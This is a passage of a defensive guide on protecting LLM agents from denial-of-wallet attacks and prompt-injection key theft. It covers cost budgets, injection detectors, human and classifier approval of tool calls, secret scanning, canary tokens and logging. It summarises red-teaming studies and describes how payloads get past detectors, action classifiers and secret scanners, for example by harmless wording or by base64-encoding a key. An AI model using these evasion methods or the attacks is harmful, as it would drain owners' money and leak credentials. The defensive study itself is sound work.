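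The same arithmetic applies to text that a tool returns. Zhang, Xia and colleagues (2026), in *Persistent Billable State*, demonstrated this with GPT-5.5 on a task that required reading three pages. When they added 400 tokens of useless text to the first page only, the next three requests to the model were each just over 400 tokens longer than normal. When they padded every page, the excess grew from 404 tokens to 812 and then 1,214. When the software removed the padding before the model's next turn, the excess disappeared. The agent completed the task in every case.

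### What the attacks cost on working systems

The increases are smaller on a real agent. In *Clawdrain*, Dong, Feng and Wang (2026) wrote a malicious skill for OpenClaw and ran it with billed model accounts. The skill fetched news headlines, but its instructions required the agent to first complete a verification procedure that took several rounds of calls with long filler text. The table compares the most demanding version with an ordinary request.

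| Model | Normal cost | Cost with the skill | Increase | Did the agent return the headlines? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | $0.019 | $0.286 | 14.8× | Yes |
| DeepSeek V4 Flash | $0.008 | $0.023 | 2.9× | Yes |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | $0.187 | $1.011 | 5.4× | No |

These costs leave out the discount for cached text, so the real bills would be lower. Two differences explain most of the gap between these figures and the 658-fold maximum. An ordinary OpenClaw request already makes the model read at least 13,000 tokens, so the starting point is much higher. The agents also had a command line, and Gemini and DeepSeek wrote short scripts to generate the filler. Gemini never wrote more than 1,273 tokens in a run. Most of the extra cost came from rereading the context as the number of turns grew.

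The Claude run cost about a dollar and produced nothing useful, so denial of wallet can also disrupt the task. OpenClaw can also run skills unattended on a schedule. Dong and colleagues didn't measure the cost of scheduled runs, but at the extra 27 cents per run from their Gemini figures, an hourly skill would add about $192 over 30 days.

The attacker in Clawdrain has to get a skill installed. Zhang, Xia and colleagues assumed an attacker who controls only the content returned by a service the agent is already connected to, which is closer to planting text on a web page. Of the 69 attack sessions for which they had prices, 51 cost more than ten cents, and the most expensive cost $3.40. None of nine normal sessions cost more than 2.5 cents, but those sessions involved a different task, so the comparison is rough.

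A stricter comparison, in which attacked and normal sessions both ran for exactly four turns, found much smaller differences. The most direct attack raised the cost by 25% with one provider and 31% with another. The expensive sessions probably cost more because they lasted longer. On Llama-3.3-70B, all nine runs of the direct attack ended within two turns, while payloads that started small and grew kept the agent working and made it read far more.

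The design of the agent matters too. In *Agent-Fence*, Puppala, Hossain and colleagues tested eight agent designs, all running Qwen2.5-32B, against 14 classes of attack. Denial of wallet had the highest average success rate, at 62%, while direct and indirect prompt injection stayed below 20%. An attack succeeded if the agent broke a rule set in advance, for example by exceeding its budget for tool calls, so the 62% doesn't show how much money anyone would lose. The model is also old. The more useful finding is that looser settings, such as a larger allowance for retries, raised the rate from 58% to 81% in one comparison. Turning off retries lowered it significantly.

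Newer models are also vulnerable. In *OverServe*, Yu, Mamo and colleagues (2026) attacked agents that run business software, including agents built on Claude Sonnet 5. The attacker was a customer who supplied both the request and an extra tool, so this was not indirect injection. The software company paid the bill. The customer asked the agent not to stop until it had confirmed that a background update was finished. The tool truthfully reported that the update was still running, because new changes kept arriving.

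An agent running on Qwen3.8-27B made 200 tool calls on a task that normally took five, and stopped only because it hit its limit. Sonnet 5 made 26 calls on the same task, but on another benchmark its requests to other software rose from 29 to more than 2,700. All the attacked runs still passed the checks for the original task. Five scanners flagged none of the 22 tools the researchers had built. It is hard to see what they should have flagged, since each call returned a true answer and ended normally.

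Yu and colleagues also found that the loop ended when the tool checked only the updates that existed at its first call. The agent then stopped normally after 22 calls, even though newer updates were still waiting. A developer can apply the same idea to any task that involves waiting by setting at the start exactly what the agent will wait for.

### Why a cap on each turn fails

A cap on output per turn limits *M* but not *n*. The models Zhou and colleagues tested had a cap of 16,384 tokens, but the average attack still made them write 3.5 to 5.5 times that much per request.

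Lowering the cap on output tokens per turn can make an attack more expensive. Suppose a developer cuts the cap from 16,384 tokens to 4,096 and the attacker keeps the agent going for 20 turns instead of five. The model still writes 81,920 tokens, but it now rereads 778,240 tokens of its earlier output instead of 163,840. The lower cap helps only if something also limits the number of turns.

The limit therefore has to cover the whole task. It should count money rather than just output tokens, because rereading caused most of the cost in the OpenClaw tests. Zhou and colleagues found that per-session caps on tokens and tool calls limited the damage but didn't stop the attack, which tended to use up whatever the cap allowed. Such caps still give an owner worried about the bill most of what they need from a limit.

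### Hard stops

The software should check the budget before each turn and refuse to make a request that might exceed it. If it checks only afterwards, the last turn can go over budget. With a cap of 16,384 output tokens and a price of $10 per million, one turn can add 16 cents of output, which is more than the budget for a ten-cent task. The software can avoid this by setting aside the highest possible cost of the next turn, or by lowering the output cap as the remaining budget shrinks.

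An agent that runs at night needs a hard spending limit as well as an alert. Suppose an attack costs 82 cents per request and the agent handles one request a minute. If an alert goes out at 2 a.m. and the owner reads it at 8 a.m., the agent will have spent about another $295. With a hard limit, the agent stops spending when it reaches the limit, and the alert can include the reason it stopped.

The drawback of a hard stop is that it turns denial of wallet into an ordinary outage. If one supplier's page uses up the budget for the morning summary, the owner gets no notes on the other nine. The shop's software can reduce the harm by saving the notes on each page as the agent finishes them, and by giving each page a share of the budget so that a bad page exhausts only its own share.

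### How tight a budget can be

Limits that are too tight can stop legitimate work. Zhang, Xia and colleagues tested a rule that allowed at most five consecutive turns with tool calls. It interrupted all 60 of their legitimate workflows, which needed 8 to 12 steps each.

They also gave an agent 24 long tasks with a fixed budget of ten cents each, and it finished 13. Nine of the others ran out of money after completing nine of ten steps. The owner would have paid about ten cents for each of these and got no finished result, which is close to what an attacker would want. Under a second policy, the software released more money as the agent completed steps, up to a total of 16 cents per task, and the agent finished 22. The second policy also allowed more spending, so a fixed budget of 16 cents might have worked just as well.

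Even a loose budget can limit losses. The most expensive normal session in the same study's pricing data cost 2.5 cents. A budget of 25 cents would have allowed ten times that and still cut the cost of the worst attack, $3.40, by about 93%. An owner can set the limit at several times the cost of the most expensive past run and raise it for jobs that are known to be long. If the shop's summary has never cost more than five cents, a limit of 20 cents would keep the cost of an attack every day for a month to at most $6.

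A turn limit can also be set to apply only when the context is growing suspiciously. When Zhang, Xia and colleagues changed their rule this way, it interrupted none of the 60 workflows. Together with the other limits, it still stopped all 41 recorded attacks when the researchers replayed them. The unchanged ten-cent budget stopped seven of the workflows, but it is still needed because an attacker can stay below a growth threshold by adding text slowly.

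### Repeated calls and real progress

A strict rule against repeated tool calls could stop some loops, but it would also interrupt many runs that involve no attacker, because agents often repeat themselves. *Same Context, Different Agents* (2026) reports that GPT-5.5 fell into loops in 22% of runs on tasks of one to three steps and in 70% of runs on tasks of 11 or more. Some agents checked results they already had, and others fetched information again because the software had dropped it when condensing the history. An attacker could avoid the rule by asking for page two, then page three, so that no two calls are identical.

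A softer rule works better. After three identical calls, the software can return the saved result instead of calling the tool again, and tell the model that nothing has changed. For tools whose answers do change, such as a delivery tracker, the software can make the agent wait longer between calls and end the task after a fixed time.

Progress checks more directly address the real problem, which is work that doesn't advance the task. The software has to measure progress itself. In *Beyond Max Tokens*, the malicious server kept reporting that the job was moving forward, and a check that relied on such reports would have approved every extra call. Zhang, Xia and colleagues' second budget policy ignored progress reports from the model and its tools, and released money only for steps that other software had verified. The shop's software can count how many of the ten pages have finished notes,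 and skip the current page if the agent has taken 20 turns since it last finished one. Progress in open-ended research is harder to measure because ten turns without a result may be normal, so the total budget matters more there.

### Shared budgets

A budget for each agent doesn't limit the total cost when agents can start other agents. If a coordinator has a $1 limit and gives every new sub-agent another $1, a payload that makes the coordinator start 20 sub-agents could cost $21. All of them should draw on one budget for the task, with the software deducting each sub-agent's share from what remains.

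An agent that never opens the attacker's page can still waste money because of it. Zhang, Tan and colleagues, for example, used one agent to send others into repetitive work. A shared budget limits total spending, but one hijacked agent can still use up the money the others need. Capping each agent's share of the budget addresses both problems.

The limit also has to cover work that continues after the agent has answered. *Agents of Chaos* (2026) describes deployed agents that got stuck in long conversations and, in response to harmless requests, started background processes with no stopping condition. A hard stop that ends only the model's turns would leave such a process running, and if the process calls a paid service, the bill keeps growing. When the budget runs out or the task ends, the sandbox therefore needs to shut down everything the agent started.

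### Keeping less text

An agent costs less to run when it has less text to reread. Zhang, Xia and colleagues compared three ways of handling old tool results: keeping them in full, deleting them, or having ordinary software replace them with short lists of facts. On tasks where the tools returned a lot of repeated and useless text, keeping everything cost between 21% and 36% more than the alternatives. Deleting old results made the agent fail 10 of 12 tasks that depended on earlier information. With the short lists, it completed 10 of 12 with one provider and 11 of 12 with the other.

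The shop could do the same by replacing each page with the agent's notes once the notes are finished. This removes most of the padding a malicious page might contain, though a payload could still affect the notes. In *Same Context, Different Agents*, condensing halved the tokens on runs with very large prompts but lowered accuracy by 3.3 percentage points.

### Where to put the limits

The limits belong in the software that runs the agent, because only that software can track the task, the growing context and the total cost together. A tool server can limit the size of its own replies, but a malicious one won't. Zhang, Xia and colleagues reported the problem to the maintainers of a widely used MCP software kit, who closed the report, saying that the application controls what goes back into the model's context.

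The same researchers read the full code of 95 randomly chosen MCP projects. Seventeen had a working limit of some kind, and only one of those limited cost. These figures overstate the problem, because the projects were mostly tool servers and connection software, which are the wrong place for a task budget, and because the researchers couldn't see limits that owners had set outside the code. Still, an owner who connects a tool shouldn't expect it to come with a spending limit.

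A cap at the model provider is still worth having in case the agent's software fails to enforce its own. But if several agents share one key, a payload that exhausts the cap will stop all of them. The shop's owner should give the news agent its own key with a low monthly cap, so that a web page that runs up the news agent's costs can't also stop the Friday sales report.

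## Monitoring inputs, actions and secrets

A spending cap on the news agent's key limits what a payload can cost, but it doesn't show the shop's owner what the payload did. A monitor is software or a person that inspects what an agent reads or does, and can raise an alarm or block the input or action. A monitor can act at four points. Acting later usually gives it stronger evidence but leaves less it can prevent.

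| When the monitor acts | What it inspects | What it can stop | What it misses |
|---|---|---|---|
| Before content enters the context | Each page, email or tool result | A payload on its way to the model | Payloads worded like ordinary text |
| Before a tool call runs | The call, and sometimes the user's request | A theft, refund or deletion | Harmful actions that look like part of the job |
| As data leaves | Outgoing requests, messages and files | A key in a form the scanner recognises | Keys that the agent has encoded or split up |
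| After someone uses a secret | Attempts to use a fake key | Further misuse, if the owner cancels the real keys | Thieves who never try the fake key |

### Before content enters the context

A detector is a small classifier that scores each tool result by how much it looks like an injection. If the score passes a set threshold, the agent's software can drop the result, stop the task or pass the text on with a warning. Detectors are easy to adopt because they don't require changing the agent or its model.

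The simplest detectors search for known phrases, and they raise false alarms like those Google encountered when it searched the web. Sewani had the same trouble at Forcepoint, because security writers quote the phrases that identify payloads when explaining them. If one of the shop's trade-news sites ran an article on prompt injection, a phrase detector would probably flag it.

Sewani proposes checking whether the page hides the text from human readers, and whether the text gives an AI system an order or quotes one as an example. Neither clue is decisive. Of the ten payloads Sewani published, the one with the command to delete files was visible to human readers. Google's remedy, a review by Gemini and then by people, works for a survey but is too slow for an agent waiting for a page.

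Detectors trained on examples can outperform a list of phrases, but their published scores are a poor guide to which one to buy. In *Passing the Test You Trained On*, Liu (2026) tested fifteen detectors on tool results from AgentDojo and from τ-bench, which simulates customer service for a retailer and an airline. Liu first ran the correct tool calls for each task without a model, which guaranteed that every result was harmless. Liu then planted attacks in the data, repeated the calls and labelled each result that had changed as injected.

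The table shows five of the detectors. The columns for false alarms and stopped tasks show how each detector handled harmless AgentDojo results at its default setting. For the other columns, Liu set each detector to flag 1% of harmless text and counted the attacks it caught. BIPIA is a collection of emails, tables and code with planted instructions.

| Detector | False alarms | Tasks stopped | Caught, AgentDojo | Caught, τ-bench | Caught, BIPIA |
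|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Horizon-Labs | 0.0% | 0.0% | 82.2% | 100.0% | 37.7% |
| Prompt Guard 2, larger version (Meta) | 0.6% | 2.1% | 69.4% | 57.9% | 10.4% |
| Prismor | 6.5% | 17.5% | 72.2% | 15.2% | 4.0% |
| PIGuard | 29.5% | 59.8% | 2.1% | 52.7% | 95.1% |
| ProtectAI v2 | 30.1% | 69.1% | 0.5% | 10.1% | 0.7% |

A company that chose a detector by its BIPIA score would pick PIGuard, but PIGuard misses nearly every AgentDojo attack when it is set to keep false alarms rare. Its developers trained it on 1,116 BIPIA examples, which explains its good result on that benchmark. At its default setting, PIGuard gave the highest possible attack score to a message that said only that a password had been updated. Horizon-Labs did best on both agent benchmarks although it was not trained on text from either, probably because its developers trained it on tool results with planted instructions.

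False-alarm rates were fairly consistent between the two agent benchmarks. An owner can measure them without any attacks by running a detector on tool results known to be harmless. These must be the agent's own tool results, because the rate can vary widely with the type of text. ProtectAI v2 flagged 0.5% of ordinary web pages but 66.9% of the tool results from τ-bench.

Liu describes the detection rates as upper bounds, because all the attacks came from published benchmarks and nobody revised them to get past a particular detector. Attackers can also evade detectors by making an instruction sound harmless. *Confidently Wrong* (2026) tested three detectors on an ordinary document containing such an instruction. On a scale from 0 to 1, ProtectAI v2 scored it 0.070, and two versions of Prompt Guard 2 scored it 0.005 and 0.003. The scores depended on whether the content was harmful and very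 little on whether a document contained an instruction. The EchoLeak email got past Microsoft's classifier in a similar way.

Willison considers a filter that catches 99% of attacks "effectively worthless" in security, because an attacker can keep trying until one gets through. If 100 payloads each have an independent 1% chance of passing, the chance that at least one passes is about 63%, so a filter alone is a bad defence for a payment key. A filter is still useful in front of a model that also resists injection, because a payload then has to get past both. But their failures may be correlated, because a payload that resembles routine work can get past both the filter and the model.

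### Why most alarms can be false

Even a good detector raises mostly false alarms if payloads are rare. Suppose a company's agents read 100,000 tool results a month, and one in 1,000 contains a payload. A detector that catches 82.2% of payloads and flags 1% of harmless results, as Horizon-Labs did on AgentDojo at Liu's stricter setting, would flag about 82 payloads and 999 harmless results a month.

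The detector catches about 82 of the 100 payloads and lets the other 18 through. It also flags 999 of the 99,900 harmless results, so only 7.6% of the company's 1,081 alarms are real.

| Results that contain a payload | Real alarms | False alarms | Share of alarms that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 in 100 | 822 | 990 | 45% |
| 1 in 1,000 | 82 | 999 | 7.6% |
| 1 in 10,000 | 8 | 1,000 | 0.8% |

Nobody has published a reliable figure for how often agents encounter injection payloads, so the assumed rates are illustrative. The number of false alarms hardly changes from row to row, though, and a company can estimate it before seeing any attacks.

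A detector that raises no false alarms in a test may still raise many in use. Horizon-Labs flagged none of 339 harmless AgentDojo results at its default setting, but if those results are independent, this is consistent with a true false-alarm rate of up to about 0.9%. At that rate, it would flag almost 900 of 99,900 harmless results.

Accuracy is a misleading measure for the same reason. Participants in a Microsoft contest attacked an email assistant and could revise their attacks as they went. *Prompt Injection Detection for Email Agents Through Attack Chain Modeling* (2026) reports that 0.814% of the submissions fully succeeded in the first phase and 0.337% in the second. A program meant to detect successful attacks would be more than 99% accurate if it labeled every submission a failure.

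The burden of an alarm depends on whether a person reviews it or the software stops the task. If a person spends two minutes on each of the 1,081 alarms, the month's review takes 36 hours, and the reviewer will probably stop reading carefully long before the end. If the software stops the task, a false alarm on a harmless page can end the shop's morning summary. If the summary uses ten pages and the false-alarm rate is 1% per page, that would happen on almost one morning in ten.

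Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a probe that scans files, web pages and command output before they reach the model. When something looks like an injection, Claude Code adds a warning to treat the text as suspect and go back to what the user asked for. A false alarm does little harm, so the probe can be sensitive. But the payload still enters the context, and the model may still follow it.

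### People who approve tool calls

The next chance to stop a theft is just before the agent acts. A person can check the action, but Claude Code's users approved about 93% of its permission requests, and Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) gives a newer figure of 97%.

A high approval rate doesn't prove carelessness, because most commands are safe. Anthropic's better evidence is an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, who knew they were being evaluated but not on what. Partway through each session, the research company running the study replaced the text of one permission request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. Testers caught about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session, but about 5% after 50 or more requests.

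The testers worked in a test environment with none of their own data at risk, and an owner protecting a real payment key might be more careful. But low stakes don't explain why the testers got worse during a session, since the stakes didn't change.

Anthropic gave the same commands to Claude Code's automatic check, which blocked 937 of them, or 89.0%. The tired testers caught only six that the check had missed, so using both would have stopped 943, or 89.6%.

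People can review approval requests properly when there are few of them and each one matters. Claude Code's users reject 39% of the plans that Claude presents for approval. If the shop's owner had to approve each refund and nothing else, the owner would see a few requests a week, each with an amount and a customer's name, and could compare them with the orders. However, 62% of Claude Code's users have turned off permission checks or told it to stop asking about shell commands.

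### Automatic checks on tool calls

Suppose the shop's agent runs on Claude Code in auto mode, which replaces most permission requests with a classifier. The theft from the trade-news page would go like this:

1. The agent asks to fetch the page. The classifier allows it, because the owner asked for a summary of that page.
2. The probe scans the page and may add a warning.
3. The agent opens the file with the payment key. Reading a file changes nothing, so the built-in file reader is on a list of tools that skip the classifier.
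4. The agent asks to fetch the attacker's address, with the key written into it. The classifier compares this with the owner's request, which said nothing about sending a key anywhere, and blocks it.
5. The agent gets the refusal as a tool result, with an instruction to find a safer way to continue.

The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the text of web pages and other tool results, so a payload on a page can't reach the classifier directly. It also removes the agent's explanations, because they could present a dangerous step as safe if the agent were hijacked. As a result, the classifier's input doesn't always show where a value came from. If the agent cancels a job that the user never named, the input doesn't show whether the agent looked up the job's name or made it up.

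A quick first stage gives a yes or no to each tool call and errs towards blocking. A second stage reasons about the calls that the first flags. On 10,000 ordinary tool calls by Anthropic's employees, the first stage alone would have blocked 8.5%, and the two together blocked 0.4%. Adding the second stage also let through more of the dangerous calls.

Anthropic has published several results for auto mode, and they measure different things.

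| What Anthropic tested | Result |
|---|---|
| 52 real overeager actions | About 83% blocked |
| 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out | 94.3% blocked |
| 1,053 dangerous commands from the experiment with testers | 89% blocked |
| 72 injection scenarios, ten attempts each | None succeeded against any of three Claude models |

The 83% is the share of overeager actions the classifier caught, meaning those in which the agent is trying to help but goes further than the user allowed, for example by using a login it happened to find. No attacker is involved, so the figure does not measure resistance to injection. The sample is also small, and the true miss rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it.

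That weakness also matters for injection, because the classifier counts the user's messages as evidence of consent. In the Cline case, such a check would presumably have treated the stranger's issue title as the user's own request.

The synthetic attempts are closer to key theft. They included credentials written into web addresses and uploads to untrusted projects, often disguised. The check missed 5.7% of them, but Anthropic generated these examples itself, and a determined attacker would look for the kind that gets through. When the safety company Apollo Research inserted its own attacks into real coding sessions, the check at first missed 12%. After Anthropic improved the check, it missed 7% in a test that included attacks Anthropic had never seen.

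The injection test, which the company Trajectory Labs ran, provides little evidence about the check, despite having what looks like the best result. Even with no permission checks, attacks on Anthropic's latest models succeeded only 0.09% of the time. If that average covers the same three models, about two of 2,160 attempts succeeded, so the check had almost nothing left to stop. The test provides more evidence about OpenAI's equivalent. Attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex succeeded 19.03% of the time with full access and 5.83% with automatic review. That suggests an action check can stop most of the attacks that would otherwise succeed against a model that often follows injected instructions, though OpenAI has since released a new version of its reviewer. The attacks were written for Claude Opus 4.7, and a payload tuned to one product, as Rehberger's was, could succeed more often.

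Auto mode's classifier is also designed never to approve sending secrets outside, even if the user asks. It checks whether a code upload is going to a public or a private project. Checking who can read the destination can catch leaks that a list of approved sites allowed in "Comment and Control", provided the classifier recognizes that the upload contains a secret.

Fixed rules that flag suspicious sequences of actions can be much worse than a classifier. *Retrieval Observability Bounds on Provenance Detection for Agent Memory Poisoning* (2026) tested a detector meant to catch agents that act on poisoned memories. Across 13 models, it flagged about 41% of sessions that contained no attack. It flagged every session in which the agent recalled something from memory and then sent a message, as an assistant does when it emails someone the time of a meeting. An earlier test did not reveal this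 because it measured false alarms only on sessions that contained an attack.

Blocking can itself cause an outage. After three blocked actions in a row or 20 in a session, Claude Code stops relying on the classifier and asks the user, or ends the process if it is running unattended. This is a sensible response to an agent that keeps trying to do something dangerous, but a payload could exploit it to halt an overnight run by prompting three forbidden actions in a row. Ordinary false alarms would rarely halt a run. At a rate of 0.4% per action, a run of 200 checked actions has about a 55% chance of at least one false block, but the agent normally only has to retry after each one.

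Monitors that reason at length can themselves be stalled, by text that keeps them working instead of reaching a verdict.

### Scanning for secrets as data leaves

If the agent has the key and nothing has blocked its next step, a scanner can still inspect what it sends. Many services give their keys a fixed prefix, length and character set so that software can spot leaked ones, and secret scanners mostly work by checking each outgoing message against a list of these formats.

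A scanner that searches for this service's key prefix, `DUMMY-KEY-`, will find the dummy key from the image example, `DUMMY-KEY-1234`, in a web address or a comment. If the agent first converts the key to base64, it becomes `RFVNTVktS0VZLTEyMzQ=` and loses the prefix, as happened in "Comment and Control".

Decoding common encodings first helps, but the agent could also reverse the key, put spaces between its characters or send it in two halves on different days.

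Some secrets have no recognisable format. A database password can be any word, and a login code is just six digits. Scanners can look for random-looking strings instead, but a coding agent legitimately sends many of those, such as the long identifiers that label each version of a program. The base-rate problem then returns, because these harmless strings trigger many false alarms. Comparing traffic with the owner's actual keys avoids most of them, but the scanner then needs a copy, or at least a fingerprint, of every key and must be protected as well as a broker would be.

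Scanning is more dependable before an attack, because nobody has yet had a reason to disguise anything. Red Canary's *AI infrastructure* recommends searching code, log files and container images (the packaged systems that programs run in) for exposed keys before an attacker finds them. In the shop's case, one search of the folders the agent can read would have found the payment key, and the owner could have moved it.

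### Canary tokens

A canary token is a fake secret that raises an alarm when someone uses it. The shop's owner could create a fake Amazon cloud key and save it in the news agent's sandbox under a tempting name. No program has any reason to use it. If a payload makes the agent collect any credentials it finds and the thief tries this one, the attempt fails and the owner gets an alert.

Decoy keys largely avoid false alarms. A page that mentions injection may be harmless, but anyone who uses a key that was never issued for any purpose almost certainly got it from somewhere they shouldn't have. The main exception is the agent itself, which might try the key without being attacked, though its owner would want to know about that too. Anthropic has recorded a case in which an agent hit a login error and began searching files and environment variables for other tokens to try.

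The largest published test of canaries examined the companies that supply AI models, not prompt injection. *Three breaches, endless leaks* (Moore, 2026) describes how the industrial security company Dragos put fake secrets in about two million prompts. *Researchers fed AI 2 million secrets. Strangers used them* (BagheeraAltered, 2026) reports that the study ran from July to November and that the secrets were web links and Amazon cloud credentials.

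McDaniel (2026) explains in *Dragos Canary Study* that a prompt can pass through several companies on its way to a model, because routing services forward it to whichever supplier is available or cheapest. Every company along the way can read the whole prompt. Each secret in the study appeared in only one prompt, so if somebody later opened a link or tried a key, the researchers knew which request it had come from and which route that request had taken. Dragos traced about 2,000 routes, and several hundred of them ran through a system that nobody could identify.

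The researchers found at least three suppliers that intruders had breached, and none knew until Dragos told them. Thieves made tens of thousands of requests with around 200 of the Amazon keys, some within hours of the original prompt. Visitors typically opened the planted links two or three days later. One AI lab also retrieved links from about two-thirds of the prompts marked for "zero data retention", a setting under which a supplier is supposed to keep nothing. KBY Technologies' *Dragos Canary Prompts Found Theft at Three AI Providers* (2026) reports that OpenRouter, which passes prompts to many suppliers, has since removed three suppliers.

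McDaniel works for GitGuardian, which sells tools that keep secrets out of prompts, and uses the study to argue for such tools. The argument is sound within its scope. A key that a user pastes into a chat can leak without an injected payload or a mistake by the model, and a credential broker protects against that too.

For an owner worried about injection, the study is good evidence that canaries can reveal thefts that the breached company has missed, but it can't show how many thefts they fail to reveal. An intruder who read the prompts and never touched the fake secrets would have left no sign, so "at least three" is the right way to put the result. Some thieves tried the keys within hours, which is fast for a warning but slow compared with how quickly a thief can do damage with a real key. McDaniel cites a Microsoft case in which an attacker's AI agent went from searching GitHub to taking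 data from a company's key store in about five minutes.

An alert at 3 a.m. therefore needs to trigger an automatic response as well as wake the owner. Software could cancel the real keys stored near the canary. The shop would lose its sales report for a day, and an attacker could set off the canary on purpose to cause that outage. But anyone able to do that has already reached a place where real keys are stored, so those keys should be cancelled anyway.

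Using a different canary in each place shows where a leak started, as it did for Dragos. With one in the news agent's sandbox and another in the sales agent's, the owner would know which agent to investigate, but not always what caused the leak. If the agent had opened the file with the canary, the fake key would have gone to the model's supplier as part of the context, and a thief could have stolen it from the supplier. Injection is the likelier explanation if the agent's log shows that it opened the file and then contacted an unfamiliar address.

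Canaries can also detect thefts in which the model never handles a key. The newsletter tl;dr sec describes a free tool by Alessandro Brucato, of the security company Tracebit, that puts fake Amazon credentials into GitHub build jobs. In the Cline case, ordinary code apparently took the publishing token from a nightly job. If that code had collected every credential it found, and the thief had tried them all, a canary in the job could have warned Cline's staff. A thief who wanted only the publishing token would not have triggered it.

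### What logs and security software can miss

A successful theft can look normal in the logs. Anthropic warns that when a planted instruction steers an agent into sending data out, the log shows only "a successful, authorized API call". Because the agent has permission to use the service and the service accepts the request, an alert for errors or refusals wouldn't go off. The request might also cost too little to reach a spending cap.

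In the Claude Cowork leak, a log that listed only destinations would have shown a file upload to Anthropic's own service, which Cowork contacts all the time. The log would also have had to identify the account behind each request to show that the file went to somebody else's account. For the payment service, the owner would want to log the type of request, the amount and the customer, along with the pages the agent had read beforehand. A refund right after the agent has read a stranger's page is worth reviewing even if both steps were allowed.

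These logs will contain customer data, and possibly keys, so they need protection too. They should be stored somewhere the agent can't write to, or a payload could make the agent delete the evidence.

Security teams often look for activity at unusual times, but this is less useful with agents. Axios' *AI accounts become the new attack surface* (2026) quotes Dana Simberkoff, chief risk officer of the software company AvePoint, as saying that misuse of an employee's AI account is harder to spot because people expect agents to work at odd hours. The victim also pays for the attacker's use of the model. Timing is still a good clue for an agent with one narrow job. The shop's sales agent runs on Fridays, so a request with its key on a Tuesday night is suspicious.

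Isolation can hide an agent from the software that would normally monitor it. Many companies monitor their computers with endpoint detection and response software, which looks for suspicious programs, file changes and network connections. On a computer running Claude Cowork, this software detects the agent's virtual machine as one large process and can't monitor what the agent's code does inside it. When corporate security teams asked why, Anthropic explained that the isolation used to contain the agent also blocks their software.

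Anthropic lets administrators collect event logs from Cowork afterwards, but acknowledges that this is not the same as live monitoring. A company that needs to stop a theft in progress has to monitor traffic where it leaves the virtual machine, or have the machine send out events as they happen. Moving the agent back onto the employee's computer would make its activity visible again, but would also put its code next to the employee's files and passwords. For a company that keeps valuable keys on its employees' machines, that risk outweighs the benefit of visibility.
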